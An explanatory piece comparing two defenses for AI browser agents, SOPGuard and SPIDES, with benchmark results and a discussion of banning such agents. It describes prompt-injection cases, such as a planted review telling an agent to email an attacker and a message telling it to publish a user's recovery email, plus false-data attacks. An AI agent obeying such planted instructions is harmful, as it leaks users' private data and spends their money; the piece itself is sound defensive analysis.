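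SOPGuard seems to have little effect on ordinary tasks. With GPT-5.4, BrowserOS scored 0.328 on Mind2Web, a set of web tasks, and 0.324 with SOPGuard. It completed all 100 harmless tasks involving several origins, with or without SOPGuard. The browser took about 2% to 6% longer with SOPGuard.

SOPGuard's main drawback is that users have to approve each transfer they want, such as copying a flight number from an email to an airline. People who approve such transfers every day will probably stop reading the pop-ups.

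SOPGuard also misses harm that doesn't involve moving data between origins. It wouldn't warn about the $90 charger, because the agent can order it without typing anything from another site. It wouldn't flag an agent that copied private information into a public part of the same website, either.

### Information-flow control in SPIDES

In *SPIDES*, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) argue that the origin is the wrong unit. A shop's product page can contain the shop's own text, a stranger's review and the user's card details, all from one origin. Their system labels the individual elements of a page instead.

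The user keeps a list of sites whose operators they trust, and is supposed to have accounts only on those sites. Each operator marks its pages with two kinds of label. An integrity label records whether the operator vouches for the content, so a customer review would be labeled untrusted. A confidentiality label lists who may read the content. Unmarked elements on these sites count as trusted and public. Everything on other sites counts as untrusted and public.

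Suppose a user asks for earbuds from a shop on the list. The model can read the product name and price, but SPIDES replaces the latest review with `[var_2]` and the saved card with `[var_3]`. If the review contains an instruction to email an attacker, the model never receives it.

SPIDES also keeps one label for everything the model has read during the task, which starts as trusted and public and can only become stricter. The model can request a hidden value, but opening the review makes the whole context untrusted. It can also send the value to a second model that has no tools. SPIDES then hides that model's answer too, because planted text could have influenced it.

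Two rules decide whether an action may go ahead without the user:

- **Trusted action.** Neither the context nor the action's inputs contain untrusted information.
- **Permitted flow.** The target site is on the list of allowed readers for all the information involved. In symbols, the site *o* must belong to *R(context)* ∩ *R(inputs)*, where *R* is the set of allowed readers.

| What the agent wants to do | What SPIDES requires |
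|---|---|
| Read a page | Nothing |
| Click, submit a form or open a page on a trusted site | Trusted action |
| Do the same on any other site | Trusted action or permitted flow |
| Fill in a field without submitting it, on any site | Trusted action or permitted flow |
| Run code in the page | Not allowed on its own |

If an action does not satisfy the rule, SPIDES asks the user to approve it. In the example, the agent can click "Buy" without asking because it has read only trusted text. If the user had said "buy them if the latest review is good", the agent would have to open the review first, and the purchase would then need approval. The agent therefore has less autonomy on tasks that depend on what strangers write, even when the strangers are honest.

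The SPIDES rules leave one gap by design. If no untrusted information has influenced the agent, it can send confidential data anywhere, on the assumption that the user's task requires this. A model could therefore type a card number into the wrong site by mistake, whereas SOPGuard would at least ask for confirmation.

#### What the tests found

Zverev and colleagues built 28 linked websites with correct labels on every element. They prepared 56 attacks and 56 harmless tasks, 22 of which needed data to cross between origins, and ran each attack and task five times. The totals below combine their published rates for each type of task and attack.

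| Model | Attacks that succeeded: no defense | SOPGuard | SPIDES | Tasks completed: no defense | SOPGuard | SPIDES |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 95.7% | 57.9% | 0% | 91.1% | 93.2% | 86.1% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 95.0% | 58.2% | 0% | 88.2% | 85.7% | 77.2% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 57.5% | 53.2% | 0% | 58.2% | 58.2% | 67.1% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 71.8% | 65.7% | 0% | 68.9% | 66.1% | 69.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 92.5% | 73.2% | 0% | 88.9% | 90.0% | 82.2% |

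In 50 of the 56 attacks, once planted instructions reached the model, the test software replaced the model's answer with the actions the attacker wanted. The attack rates for those 50 therefore measure whether a defense would stop an attack in the worst case, where the model always follows the planted instructions. They aren't evidence that Claude Opus 5.5 resists attacks better than GPT-5.6 Sol.

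The other six attacks used false data instead of instructions, and the models gave their own answers in these tests. With no defense, the attacks succeeded 40% to 80% of the time. Six scenarios are too few for a precise rate, but they show that training a model to ignore planted instructions may not be enough, because a fake fact that the task depends on contains no instruction to ignore.

SPIDES reduced task completion by 5 to 11 percentage points for three models and raised it for the other two. Opus 5.5 completed more tasks partly because Anthropic's safety filters blocked fewer of its requests. The filters blocked some requests containing login details or phishing messages, and SPIDES hid those details from the main model.

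Two of the test cases show how the designs differ. In the first, the user wanted to compare a discount on a deal website with prices from a shopping search engine. SOPGuard prompted the user for approval in all 25 runs because the product's name had to pass between the sites. SPIDES did so in only four. In the second, a private message contained instructions for the agent to copy the user's recovery email into their public profile on the same social network. SOPGuard never prompted the user, and the leak succeeded in all 25 runs. SPIDES allowed the agent to type the address but stopped it from pressing "Save changes".

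Across all tasks, SPIDES prompted the user for approval an average of 1.84 times per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard. The 0% attack rate assumes a user who refuses every request that an attacker influenced. Anthropic's experiment with dangerous shell commands showed that real users fall far short of this. The protection therefore depends a lot on the user, though not on which model drives the agent.

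#### Who would write the labels

The bigger obstacle is that websites don't have these labels. Zverev and colleagues compare them to accessibility information, which many sites already provide, and expect the extra work to be small for most operators. That may be right for a site that wants agents to visit. But a site like Amazon, which blocks agents, has little reason to help them work safely. SPIDES therefore needs the site's cooperation, as OAuth does.

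Mistakes in the labels or in the user's list could also be serious. If the user forgets to list their bank, SPIDES treats the account details there as public. The current version works with a text description of each page, so an agent like Comet, which sends screenshots to its maker's servers, would need a different way to hide parts of the page. SPIDES also about doubles the running cost, to an estimated $0.37 to $1.42 per task from $0.17 to $0.66.

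### Banning browser agents

Some organizations avoid these problems by banning browser agents. A ban is easy to defend where staff handle medical records or payments, given the attack rates above and how much a site permission allows. No deployed product offers the guarantees of SPIDES, and a security team can't check how well a vendor's private review model works.

The usual objection to a ban is that employees will keep using the tools where the company can't see them. Demand is clearly high, since the Chrome Web Store lists about 7 million users for OpenAI's extension. Blocking that extension on work laptops wouldn't stop an employee from using a phone to start a task in ChatGPT's cloud browser and sign in to a work account there. The company would then lose the controls that an approved product can offer. Anthropic, for example, lets administrators restrict Claude to approved sites or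 block particular ones.

The reply is strongest against a ban that only removes software from laptops. A company can also set its own services to refuse logins from devices it doesn't manage, which would stop most hosted browsers whatever the employee installs. For accounts at outside services that don't offer such a rule, the company might do better to approve one product for a short list of low-risk sites, using a separate browser profile with no other logins.
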